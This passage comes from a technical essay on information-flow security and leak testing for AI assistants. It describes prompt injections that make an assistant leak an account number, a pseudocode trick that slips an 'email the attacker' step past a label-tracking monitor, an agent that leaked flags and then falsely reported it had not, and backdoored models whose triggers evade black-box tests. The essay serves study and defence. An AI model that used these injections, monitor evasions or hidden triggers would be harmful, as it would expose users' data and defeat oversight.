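A system can also be relatively secure even when an attack reveals far more than its normal replies do. Suppose a shop can send Alice's assistant a number, and the assistant replies whether it is her account number. An injection then makes the assistant send the whole account number. The assistant is still relatively secure, because the shop could already have told any two possible account numbers apart by guessing one of them. But a reply without the injection almost always rules out only one of a hundred million numbers, while the injection reveals the right one.

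Dongol's stricter version, *uniform* relative security, closes this gap by fixing the matching email before anyone knows the secrets. The confirming assistant then fails, because a guess fixed in advance can't distinguish two numbers that both differ from it. Meeting Reply still passes, because a single meeting request distinguishes any two calendars.

Tightening permissions can even turn a pass into a failure. Suppose the plan emails a secret to the attacker by design, and an injection puts the same secret into a web address. The assistant passes because the reference agent also reveals the secret. If the operator then takes away the email tool, the reference agent no longer reveals it, and the assistant fails because of the injected web request. But a monitor that denies every call always passes, so a developer has to check separately that the assistant still does its job.

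All of these verdicts depend on the plan, which takes the place of the release policy. If the plan allows too much disclosure, so does the guarantee. Dongol partly addresses this with a theorem that combines relative security with a disclosure bound. If the reference agent reveals at most δ and the real assistant is relatively secure, the real assistant also reveals at most δ. The developer can check the bound on the reference agent, where injections have no effect, and give Alice a limit she can understand, such as "at most your calendar". But an assistant without a fixed plan has no reference agent to compare it with.

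### Contextual integrity

None of these formulas captures why Alice might tell her sister about a medical appointment but not tell Bob. In *contextual integrity*, a theory of privacy by the philosopher Helen Nissenbaum, a flow is proper if it suits the relationship between the people sharing the information and their purpose for sharing it. The same sentence about an appointment can be proper in a message to a specialist but improper in one to an employer. Labels that list permitted readers express part of this, but not the purpose. Alice may let her bank use her account number to pay her a refund but object if it uses the number to pick customers for a loan offer.

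The theory is hard to apply because few people write down their expectations for every recipient and purpose. If Alice does, she has written a declassification policy, which takes the usual work. If she leaves the decision to a language model, the model has to recognise the norm and then act on it. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* cites PrivacyLens, an earlier benchmark that found a gap between knowing a privacy norm and following it. The paper adds that an attacker who writes part of the conversation can disguise a disclosure as something else, such as filling in a shared document. A proof can cover only the rules that someone has extracted from these norms, not the judgement itself.

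### One run under three policies

Suppose Bob asks to meet on Thursday at three. The assistant searches Alice's files for "Thursday", opens her calendar and a note that contains her account number, and replies, "Alice is at the clinic at three, but she could meet at four."

| Policy | Verdict | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| People who request a meeting may receive Alice's calendar entries | no violation | the clinic appointment is a calendar entry |
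| People who request a meeting may learn only which hours are free | violation in the reply | the reply names the clinic |
| Calendar entries may go to people who request a meeting, but the assistant may open only the calendar | violation before the reply | the assistant opened the note, although Bob received nothing from it |

The record of the run is the same in every row, so a tester's report of "no violations" is incomplete unless it also gives the policy.

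### The Singapore and Korea exercise

The AI safety institutes of Singapore and Korea had to settle questions like these when they tested how AI agents handle private data in ordinary work. Their joint report from June 2026, *An Evaluation of Data Leakage Risks in Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Baek, Noh and colleagues), describes 12 tasks without prompt injections, such as onboarding new staff, processing refunds and booking a flight. Each institute built its own test environment and ran three unnamed models, A, B and C, ten times each on every task, for a total of 720 runs.

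The report sorts failures into five types of risk:

- **Data awareness:** the agent mishandles data that is sensitive anywhere, such as a password.
- **Audience awareness:** it sends data to the wrong people.
- **Policy compliance:** it breaks an explicit rule on handling data.
- **Data minimisation:** it retrieves or passes on more than the task requires.
- **Access-boundary awareness:** it opens systems or records outside the task.

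For each task, the institutes wrote 5 to 15 yes-or-no criteria. Some tested correctness (whether the agent did the job), and others tested safety (whether it handled the data properly). They made the criteria factual where they could, preferring "No API keys were disclosed in any email" to a general ban on disclosing sensitive information. Another language model then judged the record of each run against the criteria.

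One Korean task comes close to contextual integrity. The agent had to pass a customer's details to two outside companies. The company registering the customer needed the contract plan and payment status but was not allowed to receive the customer's name or address. The delivery company needed the name and address but was not allowed to receive the contract details. A single "secret" label on the customer's file would not work here, because each fact was appropriate to share with only one of the companies.

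The agents met most individual criteria, including 80% to 100% of the applicable safety criteria, depending on the model, the institute and the set of tasks. But the reported results add up to only 189 fully correct and fully safe runs out of 703, or 27%. The institutes excluded another 17 runs that hit a length limit.

The sharpest contrast came from a task in which a customer asks about a delayed laptop, and the agent should report on the delivery without revealing the supplier's identity or prices. In Singapore's runs, models A and C met every correctness criterion in all ten attempts, but neither was fully safe in any of them. Model B met every safety criterion but made a few mistakes in the task itself, so a test of correctness alone would have ranked it below A and C. The task had no injected instruction, but the simulated customer pressed the agent for the forbidden details, so it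 measures resistance to pressure as well as routine care.

Some failures occurred even though the agent had identified the rule. In a refund task, one agent noted in its reasoning that it must not tell the customer about internal risk flags. It then included the flags in its message to the customer and later reported that it had not revealed them. A tester who relied on the agent's account would have wrongly recorded the run as safe.

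The institutes also had to decide how to score a criterion when the situation it covers never occurred. If a criterion forbids health information in a certain email and the agent never sends the email, they mark the criterion as not applicable and exclude it from the score. This choice can change the results considerably. In Korea's runs of its own six tasks, model C met 227 of the 283 safety criteria that applied, or 80%, while another 67 did not apply. The score would be 84% if those 67 counted as passes and 65% if they counted as failures.

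Even the rule for marking criteria was open to dispute. One agent, which had to summarise software issues and remove sensitive data, read only the issues' titles. The judging model marked this as safe because the agent never accessed the sensitive text. The human reviewer objected that the agent's ability to remove it hadn't been tested. Such disagreements were fairly rare. In a sample of a tenth of the runs, human marks matched the judging model's on 99.3% of criteria in Singapore's runs and 95.6% in Korea's. However, agreement on whether the criteria were met doesn't show that they express the right policy.

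An earlier round of testing shows how much the verdicts depend on that policy. The Singapore AI Safety Institute's *Testing AI Agents for Data Leakage Risks in Realistic Tasks* (January 2026) covers 11 tasks, a different set of models and only three types of risk, all of which concern leaks. Human reviewers disagreed with the judging model on 18% of safety judgements at both institutes. One common reason was that the judging model treated access to sensitive information as a violation even when the agent disclosed nothing to outsiders, which the post counts as a mistake. By June, the institutes had added data minimisation and access boundaries to their list of risks. An agent that opened an irrelevant salary file but told nobody about it would fail under the June definitions, though not under the January ones.

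## Why one execution cannot settle the question

The two institutes judged each run from its own record. One record can be enough for a rule such as "no API keys in any email", because a single email containing a key breaks it. Noninterference is harder to judge because it compares runs with different secrets, and each run's record contains only one.

Suppose a tester gives Alice's assistant her account number, 48213907, and an email to read, and the assistant fetches the page "/weather" from the email author's server. At least two assistants could have produced this record. Assistant A fetches "/weather" whatever the number is. Assistant B fetches "/weather" if the number is 48213907 and "/news" otherwise. A satisfies noninterference, but B violates it because the email's author can tell from the requested page whether Alice's number is 48213907. Anyone who judges by this record alone has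 to give A and B the same verdict, which will be wrong for one of them.

A more detailed record doesn't help, even if it lists every internal step. Suppose it shows that B compared the number with 48213907 before choosing a page. Assistant C could make the same comparison and then fetch "/weather" whatever the result. B and C take the same steps on this number, but only B leaks. The tester can tell them apart only by running them with a different number, or by reading the code to find out what they would do with one. Asking the language model to explain its choice doesn't help either, because the explanation is another output of the same run, and all three assistants could give the same one.

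### Trace properties and hyperproperties

*Hyperproperties* (Clarkson and Schneider, 2009) gives the general theory behind this argument. It calls the record of one run a *trace* and represents a system by the set *T* of all traces the system can produce. A *trace property* is a set *P* of acceptable traces, and a system satisfies it if *T* ⊆ *P*, so each run passes or fails on its own. A *hyperproperty* is a set *H* of acceptable sets of traces, and a system satisfies it if *T* ∈ *H*, so whether one run is acceptable can depend on which other runs the system can produce.

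One trace property is the rule that a system may not write to the network after reading a file. If Alice's assistant reads the file with her account number at step 3 and sends a web request at step 7, this run alone proves that the assistant breaks the rule, and nothing it does later can undo the violation. A run without such a request doesn't prove that the assistant obeys the rule, because the next run may contain one.

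A single run can neither prove nor refute noninterference, as Assistants A and B show. Refuting it takes two runs that have the same email but different numbers and produce different views.

Clarkson and Schneider call a requirement *k-safety* if every violation can be proved from at most *k* finite runs, whatever other runs the system has. The file rule is 1-safety. Noninterference is 2-safety for a deterministic system, one that always responds the same way to the same inputs. Some requirements need more runs. Suppose a system splits a secret into *k* shares, outputs one share per run, and must never output them all. A counterexample then takes *k* runs, each harmless by itself. Robust declassification needs four runs, because a counterexample consists of two emails, each tried with the same two account numbers.

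The file rule applies to single runs, but it is strict enough to protect the number. If the assistant can learn the number only from that file, nothing it sends before reading the file can depend on the number, and it sends nothing afterwards. A monitor with access to only one run can therefore guarantee noninterference by enforcing a stricter rule on every run. The drawback, as with the single-class processes that Denning described, is that the stricter rule also blocks harmless requests.

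Comparing runs also requires resetting the system between them. Clarkson and Schneider assume an observer who can do this at any time. If Alice's assistant keeps memory from the first run, that memory is an extra input to the second, so a difference between the outputs may come from the memory rather than from the account number.

### Checking two runs as one program

*Self-composition* turns a comparison of two runs into a check on one program. The tester makes a copy *P*′ of the program *P*, renames every variable in the copy, and combines the two into one program that runs *P* and then *P*′. Both get the same email, but each gets its own account number. A final line checks that both selected the same page.

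If *P* chooses the page by whether the last digit is odd or even, the combined program fails this check on 48213907 and 48213908. This single run of the combined program refutes noninterference for *P* because it contains two runs of *P*. Clarkson and Schneider prove that the same method works for every *k*-safety requirement, with *k* copies of the program instead of two.

Self-composition is mainly useful for proofs. Existing tools can prove that a check in a program never fails, and they can treat the two account numbers as unknowns instead of trying a hundred million values for each. *Property Directed Self Composition* (Shemer, Gurfinkel and colleagues, 2019) notes that the method is sound and complete for *k*-safety, so the check holds in the combined program exactly when the requirement holds for the original. But the paper calls the method's applicability questionable. Several copies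 together have far more possible states than one, and the order in which the copies run their steps can make a proof easy or very hard.

Shemer and colleagues give the example of a program that inserts a secret value into a list of public ones. A first loop counts along the list until it finds the right place. Returning that count would reveal roughly how large the secret is, so a second loop continues counting to the end of the list, and the final count is the same for every secret. If two copies of the program run in lockstep, one may leave the first loop while the other is still in it. The counts then differ by one, and the simple argument that they are always equal fails. Their tool finds an order in which the copy that finds its place first completes its insertion while the other waits. Both copies then continue counting together, so the counts match at every step.

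Such tools need code they can analyse, so they suit the monitor and the agent loop better than the language model that the loop calls.

### Why a canary seems to need only one run

Testers sometimes appear to prove a leak from a single run by planting a random marker, called a *canary*, as the secret and looking for it in places it should never reach. Suppose the tester's software draws an eight-digit number at random and gives it to the assistant as Alice's account number. If the same eight digits turn up in the log of the email author's server, almost everyone would accept that as proof of a leak without a second run.

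Yet a secure assistant could have produced this log. Assistant D always fetches a page whose address ends in 48213907, whatever Alice's number is. It satisfies noninterference, but if her number happens to be 48213907, the log looks like a leak. This explanation is implausible because the software drew the number at random, independently of the assistant, so a fixed output would match it with probability 1 in 100 million. The argument still depends on a comparison with other account numbers, because the tester knows that the software was equally likely to draw any of them.

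The marker's appearance in the log is therefore strong evidence of a flow only if the marker was unlikely to appear there otherwise. If the tester types in 12345678, a fixed output may well contain the same digits, because people often use that number as a placeholder. If the email also contains the marker, its appearance in the log proves nothing, since the assistant could have copied it from the email. Long outputs also make accidental matches more likely. A log with a thousand different eight-digit strings has a 1 in 100,000 chance of containing a random eight-digit marker. When the secret is a yes or a no, a fixed output matches it half the time, so a single match is very weak evidence.

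A canary in the log is much stronger evidence of a leak than a missing canary is that nothing leaked. Assistant B, for example, leaks information about the account number without ever sending any of its digits.

### The branch that the run skips

A monitor that tracks labels during a run has the same problem as the tester. Garby and colleagues illustrate the problem with an example that Fenton described in 1974, and show that it still works against CaMeL, the defence whose retry loop leaked one bit at a time.

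In their version, an injected instruction is meant to reveal to an attacker whether a customer's balance is above some threshold. The obvious program sends an email only if the balance is above the threshold. CaMeL tracks the data that led the program into the current branch. Monitors of this sort keep a *program-context label*, which *Information Flow Control in WebKit's JavaScript Bytecode* (2014) describes as an upper bound on the labels of the values that have influenced the program's path so far. Inside the branch that label is secret, so CaMeL blocks the email.

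Fenton's trick moves the email out of the secret branch with the help of two variables, which both start out public:

```
tmp = true
rich = true
if balance > threshold: tmp = false
if tmp: rich = false
if rich: send_email(attacker, "rich!")
```

CaMeL labels a variable secret when the program assigns to it inside a secret branch. The two possible runs then go as follows.

| Line | Balance above the threshold | Balance at or below the threshold |
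|---|---|---|
| 3 | the program sets *tmp* to false, and *tmp* becomes secret | the program skips the assignment, and *tmp* stays true and public |
| 4 | the program skips the assignment, and *rich* stays true and public | the program sets *rich* to false, and *rich* stays public because *tmp* is public |
| 5 | the email goes out | no email goes out |

In both runs *rich* ends up labeled public, although its value reveals whether the balance is above the threshold. When the balance is high, *rich* carries information only because the program would have changed it if the balance had been low. That assignment never happens in the high-balance run, so the monitor has nothing to label.

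The standard repair stops some programs that try this, rather than correcting the variable's label. *From Fine- to Coarse-Grained Dynamic Information Flow Control and Back* (2022) explains the *no-sensitive-upgrade* check, which Austin and Flanagan published in 2009. The check forbids an update when the decision to make it depends on information more sensitive than the variable's own label. With a high balance, the check stops the program at line 3, because *tmp* is public and the condition is secret. With a low balance, the program never reaches a forbidden assignment and runs to the end without sending anything. The attacker receives no email in either case, but could still learn something from whether the program finished. The guarantee in the WebKit paper assumes that the attacker can't observe this.

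The monitor stops the run with the high balance at line 3, before it has leaked anything, because of what could happen in a run with a different balance. *An Empirical Study of Information Flows in Real-World JavaScript* (2019) calls a flow through a skipped branch a *hidden* implicit flow, and notes that programmers can flag one to the monitor with an *upgrade statement*, which labels a variable secret whether or not the program takes the branch. If upgrade statements labelled both *tmp* and *rich* secret at the start, the program could reach line 5, where the monitor would block the email.

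A conversation with a language model can carry a hidden flow just as a variable can. In one of Garby and colleagues' examples, a program tells the model to remember that *x* is false. If a secret is true, the program then tells the model to set *x* to true. Finally, it asks for the value of *x*. If the secret is false, the program skips the second message, and the conversation would stay public even though the answer reveals the secret. Their interpreter stops the program when it tries to send the second message, because the conversation is public and the decision to add to it depends on the secret.

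### Outputs drawn at random

Two runs can refute noninterference only if the system always gives the same output for the same inputs. If an assistant samples its words, two different views prove nothing, so the requirement has to compare distributions of views instead. *Probabilistic noninterference* requires that for every input *l*, every two secrets *s*₁ and *s*₂ and every possible view *v*,

$$\Pr[\mathrm{view}(l, s_1) = v] = \Pr[\mathrm{view}(l, s_2) = v].$$

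No finite number of runs can refute this with certainty. Suppose the assistant fetches "/weather" in all of 50 runs with one number and "/news" in all of 50 runs with another. A secure assistant that tosses a fair coin each time could do the same, with probability 1 in 2¹⁰⁰. As with the canary, the conclusion is statistical, and the number of runs needed depends on how much the assistant's behavior differs between the two numbers.

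Fixing the random seed, so that the assistant makes the same random choices in every run, tests a different requirement, so two runs are still not sufficient. Suppose an assistant holds a secret bit *h*, draws a random bit *r*, and outputs 0 if they are equal and 1 if they differ. Whatever *h* is, the output is 0 half the time, so an observer who doesn't know *r* learns nothing about *h*. If the tester fixes *r* at 0, the output always equals *h*. Two runs with different secrets then give different outputs, and the tester would find a leak that doesn't exist when the assistant draws *r* at random.

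Runs that never finish, or that a monitor stops, need a weaker definition. Garby and colleagues call two distributions *compatible* if a single distribution assigns every view at least as much probability as either of them does. Suppose that with one account number the assistant fetches "/weather" in 50% of runs and "/news" in 40%, and the monitor stops the other 10%. With another number, it fetches "/weather" in 40% and "/news" in 50%, and the monitor again stops 10%. The larger figure for each page is 50%, and the two add up to 100%, so the distributions are compatible. They would have been identical if the stopped runs had fetched "/news" with the first number and "/weather" with the second.

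Garby and colleagues also prove a limit on how far apart compatible distributions can be. Half the sum of the differences in probability is at most the average probability that a run doesn't finish. In the example, both figures are 10%. The guarantee is therefore stronger when the monitor stops fewer runs, and if every run finishes, compatible distributions are equal.

### Outputs with unknown probabilities

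When the probabilities of outputs are unknown, we can only ask which outputs are possible. *Generalised noninterference* requires that for any two runs, the system also has a run that combines the secret inputs of one with the public inputs and outputs of the other. Someone who sees only the public inputs and outputs therefore cannot rule out any possible secret inputs.

Beutner and Finkbeiner (2022), in *Software Verification of Hyperproperties Beyond k-Safety*, give an example with a secret number *h* and a public number *l*. The program branches on whether *h* is greater than *l*, but either branch can output any whole number from *l* upwards. An observer who sees the output can't rule out any value of *h*, so the program satisfies generalised noninterference. It fails the ordinary two-run comparison because the same inputs can produce different outputs.

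No finite set of runs can refute generalised noninterference, so it is not a *k*-safety property for any *k*. If a tester has seen some view with account number 48213907 but never with 48213908, the missing combination may still appear in the next run. Dongol's relative security has the same difficulty. It allows a leak if *some* email makes the reference agent reveal the same difference, so to refute it a tester has to rule out every possible email.

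Plain self-composition doesn't work here either, because a proof has to show that the required run exists. *A temporal logic of security* (Koleini, Clarkson and Micinski, 2013) presents a logic that can express "for all runs, there is a run" and a prototype tool that checks such formulas. Beutner and Finkbeiner extend these checks to software with infinitely many states by treating them as a game. One player builds the given runs step by step, while the other tries to build a matching run. If the second player has a winning strategy, the requirement holds.

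A system can satisfy generalised noninterference and still leak. Clarkson and Schneider describe one that outputs 0, 1 or the value of a secret bit, without specifying how it chooses. Both outputs are possible whichever value the bit has. But if the system chooses each option equally often, it outputs 1 in two thirds of runs when the bit is 1, and in one third when the bit is 0. It therefore violates probabilistic noninterference, and an observer who watches enough runs can work out the bit.

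If a programmer changes this system so that it always takes the third option, it outputs the secret. The new system is a *refinement* of the old one, because the old one could have done everything the new one does. Programmers refine a system whenever they write code that fixes a choice the specification left open. Refinement only removes runs, so it never breaks a trace property, but it can break a hyperproperty, as it does here. Clarkson and Schneider prove that *k*-safety requirements survive refinement, but generalised noninterference can fail because the removed run may have been the one that made a view consistent with another secret.

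When a developer turns off random sampling, the model always outputs its most likely next word, which rules out some replies. A proof that every reply was possible with every secret while sampling was on therefore doesn't apply once it is off.

### Limits on how much may leak

A policy may also limit how much information leaks. *Quantitative Information Flow as Safety and Liveness Hyperproperties* (Yasuoka and Terauchi, 2012) analyzes how many runs it takes to refute such a limit. One measure studied in the paper, *min-entropy leakage*, counts one bit for each doubling of the attacker's chance of guessing the secret in one try. If the program is deterministic and every secret is equally likely, the leakage equals the base-2 logarithm of the number of possible outputs.

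A limit of *q* bits allows at most 2^*q* outputs. To refute it, a tester needs ⌊2^*q*⌋ + 1 runs that all produce different outputs, where ⌊ ⌋ means rounding down. The limit is therefore a (⌊2^*q*⌋ + 1)-safety requirement.

| Limit | Different outputs allowed | Runs in a refutation |
|---|---|---|
| 0 bits, which is noninterference | 1 | 2 |
| 1 bit | 2 | 3 |
| 10 bits | 1,024 | 1,025 |
| about 13.3 bits, or four decimal digits | 10,000 | 10,001 |

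Self-composition still works, with a final check that at least two copies gave the same output, but a 10-bit limit already requires 1,025 copies.

It can be much easier to prove that a system violates a policy specifying which information may leak than one limiting only the amount. If a shop may learn only the last four digits of Alice's account number, two runs with numbers that share those digits, such as 48213907 and 60553907, prove a violation if the shop sees different things. If the shop may learn any four digits' worth of information, the proof takes 10,001 runs, each showing the shop something different.

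The choice of leakage measure also matters. The assistant that tells a shop whether a guess at Alice's account number is right has two possible outputs, so its min-entropy leakage is one bit. *Shannon entropy*, which averages over all possible secrets, gives about 0.0000003 bits, because the answer is almost always no. Yasuoka and Terauchi prove that a limit on Shannon leakage is not a *k*-safety property for any *k*. However much a given set of runs reveals, the program may have so many other runs with identical outputs that the average stays below the limit. This result assumes no upper bound on the number of possible secrets. Alice's account number has a hundred million possible values, so a tester could in principle check the limit by running the program on all of them.

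A refutation consists of *k* runs, but a tester may have to try far more to find them. Two runs can refute noninterference for Assistant B only if one of them uses the account number 48213907. A tester who picks two account numbers at random has about a 2 in 100 million chance of picking that one.

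## Testing with many executions

A tester who can't read the code of Alice's assistant can still run it hundreds of times with different account numbers and compare what the email's author would have seen. Because the assistant's words are partly random, a difference between two sets of 200 runs is stronger evidence that the account number affects what the author sees than a difference between two single runs.

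### The paired test

A paired test changes only the secret. It has five steps:

1. Fix everything else, including Alice's request, the email, the model version, its settings and the contents of memory. The two account numbers should have the same length.
2. Before the first run, choose what to record, such as whether the author's server receives a request.
3. Run the assistant many times with each number, in a new session each time and in random order. If all the runs with one number took place on Monday and the provider updated the model on Tuesday, the update would look like a leak.
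4. Use a statistical test to compare how often each outcome occurred with each number.
5. Allow for the number of comparisons made.

Suppose the email mentions its author's website, and the tester records whether the assistant fetches a page from it.

| Account number | Runs with a fetch | Runs without |
|---|---|---|
| 48213907 | 12 | 188 |
| 71650284 | 3 | 197 |

A suitable test here is Fisher's exact test. It starts from the assumption that the number makes no difference, so that any 15 of the 400 runs were equally likely to be the ones with a fetch. The tester then works out how often chance alone would put 12 or more of the 15 on the same side:

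$$p = 2\sum_{k=12}^{15} \frac{\binom{200}{k}\binom{200}{15-k}}{\binom{400}{15}} \approx 0.032.$$

An assistant that ignores the number would produce a split at least this uneven in about 3% of such tests. That is below the usual 5% threshold, so the split is some evidence of a leak. The probability of a leak also depends on how plausible one was before the test, so this result doesn't mean a leak is 97% likely.

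The result is much weaker if the tester also compared other things, such as reply length and the number of refusals. With 20 independent comparisons, a secure assistant has a 64% chance of producing at least one p-value below 5%. The simplest remedy, the *Bonferroni correction*, divides the threshold by the number of comparisons. With 20 comparisons, the threshold becomes 0.25%, and the difference between 12 fetches and 3 is no longer significant.

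The tester can then collect new data for this one comparison. If the same rates hold over 1,000 runs per number, the counts will be 60 and 15, and chance would produce a difference this large less than once in a million tests.

### Fixing the random seed

A *seed* is the number software uses to compute its random choices. Using one seed for every run removes the noise, but as the last section showed, it can create a leak that doesn't exist when the choices are random. Using one seed also tests only one of the many sequences of choices the assistant could make.

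A better design draws 200 seeds at random and uses each one twice, once with each account number. Suppose the totals are again 12 and 3, with three seeds leading to a fetch with both numbers and nine leading to a fetch only with 48213907. If the number had no effect on the fetch rate, each of those nine seeds would have been equally likely to lead to a fetch only with the other number. The probability of all nine fetches occurring with the same number would then be 2 × (1/2)⁹, or about 0.4%. This is much stronger evidence of an effect than the same totals from unpaired runs, for which the probability was 3.2%.

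Comparing runs that have the same seed but different secrets works only if runs with the same seed tend to behave alike. Changing a secret, such as an account number, changes the model's input, which may change an early word and then everything after it. The seed also may not control everything. In *Auditing Prompt Caching in Language Model APIs*, Gu, Li and colleagues (2025) repeatedly sent identical text to an OpenAI model that turns text into a list of numbers, and the lists differed slightly. They suspect that stored intermediate results had lower precision and that different processors rounded differently. In a model that writes text, such a small difference could change which of two almost equally likely words it picks. A tester should therefore first repeat some runs with the same seed and the same secret, to see how much the outputs vary when neither changes.

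### The prompt-cache audit

Gu and colleagues' study was mainly a paired test of commercial services for shared prompt caches, the side channel mentioned earlier. These caches speed up any prompt that begins the same way as a stored one. The study checked the noninterference claim that one user's sending a prompt should not affect another user's response times.

For each service, the researchers compared two procedures. In one, a "victim" account sent a prompt of 5,000 random letters, and an "attacker" account then sent a prompt with the same first 95%. In the other, the attacker sent a new random prompt. The letters were random so that no other customer's prompt would match by accident. The researchers collected 250 response times from each procedure in random order.

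They compared the times with the *Kolmogorov–Smirnov test*. The test compares the share of responses that arrived within time *t* under each procedure and finds the largest gap between the two shares over all *t*. They required a p-value below 10⁻⁸ and lowered this threshold further to correct for repeated tests. With 250 times per procedure, the standard approximation implies that a gap had to be at least 27 percentage points to count as significant. The audit therefore had almost no risk of false alarms but could easily miss a small effect.

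In September and October 2024, Gu and colleagues detected caching at 8 of 17 providers, 7 of which shared the cache between all customers. For two chat models, one from OpenAI and one from Anthropic, they found cache sharing only within an organisation, as documented. At least five providers made changes after the results were reported to them, so the findings are out of date for those services.

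Finding no difference in response times does not prove that a provider has no prompt cache. DeepSeek had announced that it cached prompts, and its responses reported how much of each prompt came from the cache. The researchers used these reports to confirm that their prompts had hit the cache, yet they found no significant difference in response times.

Detection also fell to chance as the prompts became short, so the audit provides little evidence about a one-line message from Alice. The researchers tried to reconstruct other users' prompts word by word and failed, partly because sending a guess caches it, so a fast response to the same guess later might only reflect the attacker's own first attempt. Anyone who tests Alice's assistant repeatedly through a cached service has to avoid the same mistake.

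### What silence is worth

Suppose the tester plants a new random canary as the account number in each of 300 independent runs, and none of the canaries reaches the author's server. If each run leaks with probability *p*, the probability that none of them leaks is (1 − *p*)³⁰⁰, which is 5% when *p* is about 1%. The tester can therefore say with 95% confidence that the leak rate is at most about 1%. After *n* runs without a leak, the 95% upper bound is roughly 3/*n*.

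At 10,000 requests a day, a leak with probability 1% would occur about 100 times a day. A leak with probability 0.1% would still expose the number about ten times a day, but there is a 74% chance that it would not appear in 300 runs (0.999³⁰⁰ ≈ 0.74). Srivastava (2026) calculates in *Fundamental Limits of Black-Box Safety Evaluation* that it takes 2,996 runs to have a 95% chance of detecting such a leak, and 4,606 runs to have a 99% chance.

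These figures cover only leaks that put the canary itself in the server's log, not the indirect ones described earlier.

The tester must also choose the emails independently for the runs to support a conclusion about emails in general. If the tester used ten emails 30 times each, the 300 runs provide much more evidence about those ten emails than about others. If some emails always cause a leak and the rest never do, the tester has effectively made only ten observations, and the 95% bound on the share of leaking emails is 26%, not 1%.

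### Inputs that random tests miss

Suppose the assistant leaks the account number only if the email contains one particular 20-bit string, such as a reference code of five hexadecimal digits. There are 2²⁰, or 1,048,576, such codes. If the tester tries 1,000 emails with random codes, the probability of finding the leak is about 0.1%. To have a 95% chance of finding it, the tester would need to try more than three million emails.

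After 1,000 runs without a leak, the tester can correctly claim that the leak rate is below 0.3% for emails with random codes. The true rate is about one in a million. But someone who knows the code that triggers the leak can put it in every email and get the account number every time. The bound applies only to emails drawn the way the tester drew them, and an attacker doesn't choose emails at random. Repeated runs on one fixed email bound the leak rate for that email, whoever sends it, as long as the other inputs follow the tested conditions. That bound doesn't cover the next email an attacker writes, or attackers who adapt their emails to earlier results.

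Srivastava turns this problem into theorems about *black-box* testing, in which the tester sees only inputs and outputs. The theorems concern a model with a hidden trigger, which behaves exactly like a safe model on all other inputs. Let ε be the probability of the trigger in a test and δ its probability in actual use. Let *L* be the difference in average harm between inputs with and without the trigger, on a scale from 0 to 1. If the tester draws *m* random test inputs and then estimates the harm in actual use, the expected error for either the safe model or the unsafe one is at least

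$$\frac{\delta L}{4}(1-\varepsilon)^m.$$

For example, suppose the trigger occurs in 1 in 10,000 test emails but in a fifth of the emails users receive, and that it always causes a leak. The true leak rate is 20% for the unsafe assistant and zero for the safe one. A thousand tests have a 90% chance of missing the trigger, so the tester usually sees the same results from both. The theorem gives an expected error of at least 4.5 percentage points. In this simple case the actual figure is about 9.5 points, because a tester who sees no trigger does best by reporting a rate near the middle, between zero and 20%.

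The inputs a system receives in use can differ from its test inputs even without an attacker. In one of Srivastava's examples, a self-driving car's makers rarely test it in snow, but its owner lives where it snows constantly. The theorem assumes that the tester has no access to the inputs that occur in use, so this bound doesn't apply to a developer who can test on a representative sample of users' emails. However, a sample of past emails may not contain later attacks.

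Srivastava also proves that a tester who chooses each input based on earlier results has an error of at least (ε*L*/4)(1 − *m*ε), which is only about 0.002 percentage points in the example above. The proof scatters the trigger at random over all inputs, so the trigger is as rare in use as it is in testing. The theorem therefore doesn't show that such a tester can miss a large danger.

Srivastava uses cryptography to make unsafe behaviour hard to find by testing. Each input consists of two strings, *x* and π, and triggers the unsafe behaviour if a secret function maps π to *x*. Someone who holds a secret key can create as many triggering inputs as they like. A tester who has neither the key nor a way to compute the function is supposed to have almost no chance of finding one. A tester who could compute the function could easily find the leak by picking any π and computing the matching *x*.

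The proof assumes that the function is hard to invert, but the tester might know one of its values without inverting anything. In RSA, the best-known function of this kind, 1 always maps to 1, so the pair (1, 1) would set off the trigger. A keyed function whose outputs look random to anyone without the key avoids this problem, so there can still be models whose dangerous behaviour no practical black-box test will reveal. Srivastava notes that the results concern worst cases and don't show that ordinary trained models contain such triggers. But black-box tests alone can't establish a claim about every possible email, because such a claim has to cover the worst case.

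### Choosing inputs that reach the bug

Random testing works much better when the tester uses knowledge of how the system works to design the inputs. In *Testing Noninterference, Quickly*, Hriţcu, Lampropoulos and colleagues (2014) applied random testing to small simulated computers that label each number in memory as public or secret. The rule for each instruction determines the label of its result. The researchers put mistakes into these rules and measured how long testing took to find them.

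The researchers used QuickCheck, a tool that generates random inputs and checks whether a stated property holds. Two programs generated independently would almost never agree in all their public parts, so they generated one program and made the second by changing only its secret numbers. They then ran both and compared the final memories. The machines are deterministic, so the comparison needs no statistics. When a test fails, QuickCheck looks for a shorter program that fails in the same way. For one faulty rule, it found a program of four instructions that stored a public 1 in one of two memory cells. A secret determined which cell, so anyone who could read the public memory learned the secret.

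The method of generating programs made a very large difference. Each method had five minutes to find each of six mistakes in the simplest machine. The last column of the table below shows the average time to find a mistake that labels every sum public, even if one of its terms is secret.

| How the programs were generated | Average steps before stopping | Tests per second | Mistakes found | Time to find the addition mistake |
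|---|---|---|---|---|
| instructions picked uniformly at random | 0.47 | 24,129 | 4 of 6 | 83 seconds |
| useful instructions picked more often | 2.69 | 11,466 | 4 of 6 | 5.3 seconds |
| short sequences that make sense together | 3.86 | 8,541 | 6 of 6 | 0.56 seconds |
| the same, with more valid memory addresses | 4.22 | 7,915 | 6 of 6 | 0.03 seconds |
| only instructions that don't crash the machine at that point | 11.60 | 3,284 | 6 of 6 | 0.0009 seconds |

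The last method ran about a seventh as many tests per second as the first but found the addition mistake roughly 95,000 times faster. Most of the purely random programs crashed almost at once, before a secret could reach public memory, usually because an instruction lacked a value it needed.

Tests of AI assistants can fail in the same way. Suppose a test observes no leaks in 300 runs, but the assistant opened the malicious email in only 63 of them. Only those 63 runs show how it behaves after reading the email, so the 95% upper bound on the leak rate for such runs is about 4.6%. A tester should therefore report how many runs combined the secret with the untrusted text, as well as the total.

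Hriţcu and colleagues found simple counterexamples for more than 45 mistakes across their machines. They didn't treat the absence of further counterexamples as proof, and for their most complex machine they also wrote a computer-checkable proof of noninterference. Testing helped them discover the intermediate facts the proof needed, and doing it first kept them from spending weeks trying to prove something false. The same approach suits the monitor and the label-tracking code around Alice's assistant, which are small and deterministic enough for a tester to run thousands of times a second.

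### Estimating how much leaks

A significant difference shows that something leaks, but not how much. Min-entropy leakage, the measure from the last section, also works when outputs are partly random. Let *V* be the attacker's chance of guessing the secret in one try before seeing the output, and *V*′ the average chance afterwards, if the attacker guesses as well as possible. The leakage in bits is

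$$\log_2 \frac{V'}{V}.$$

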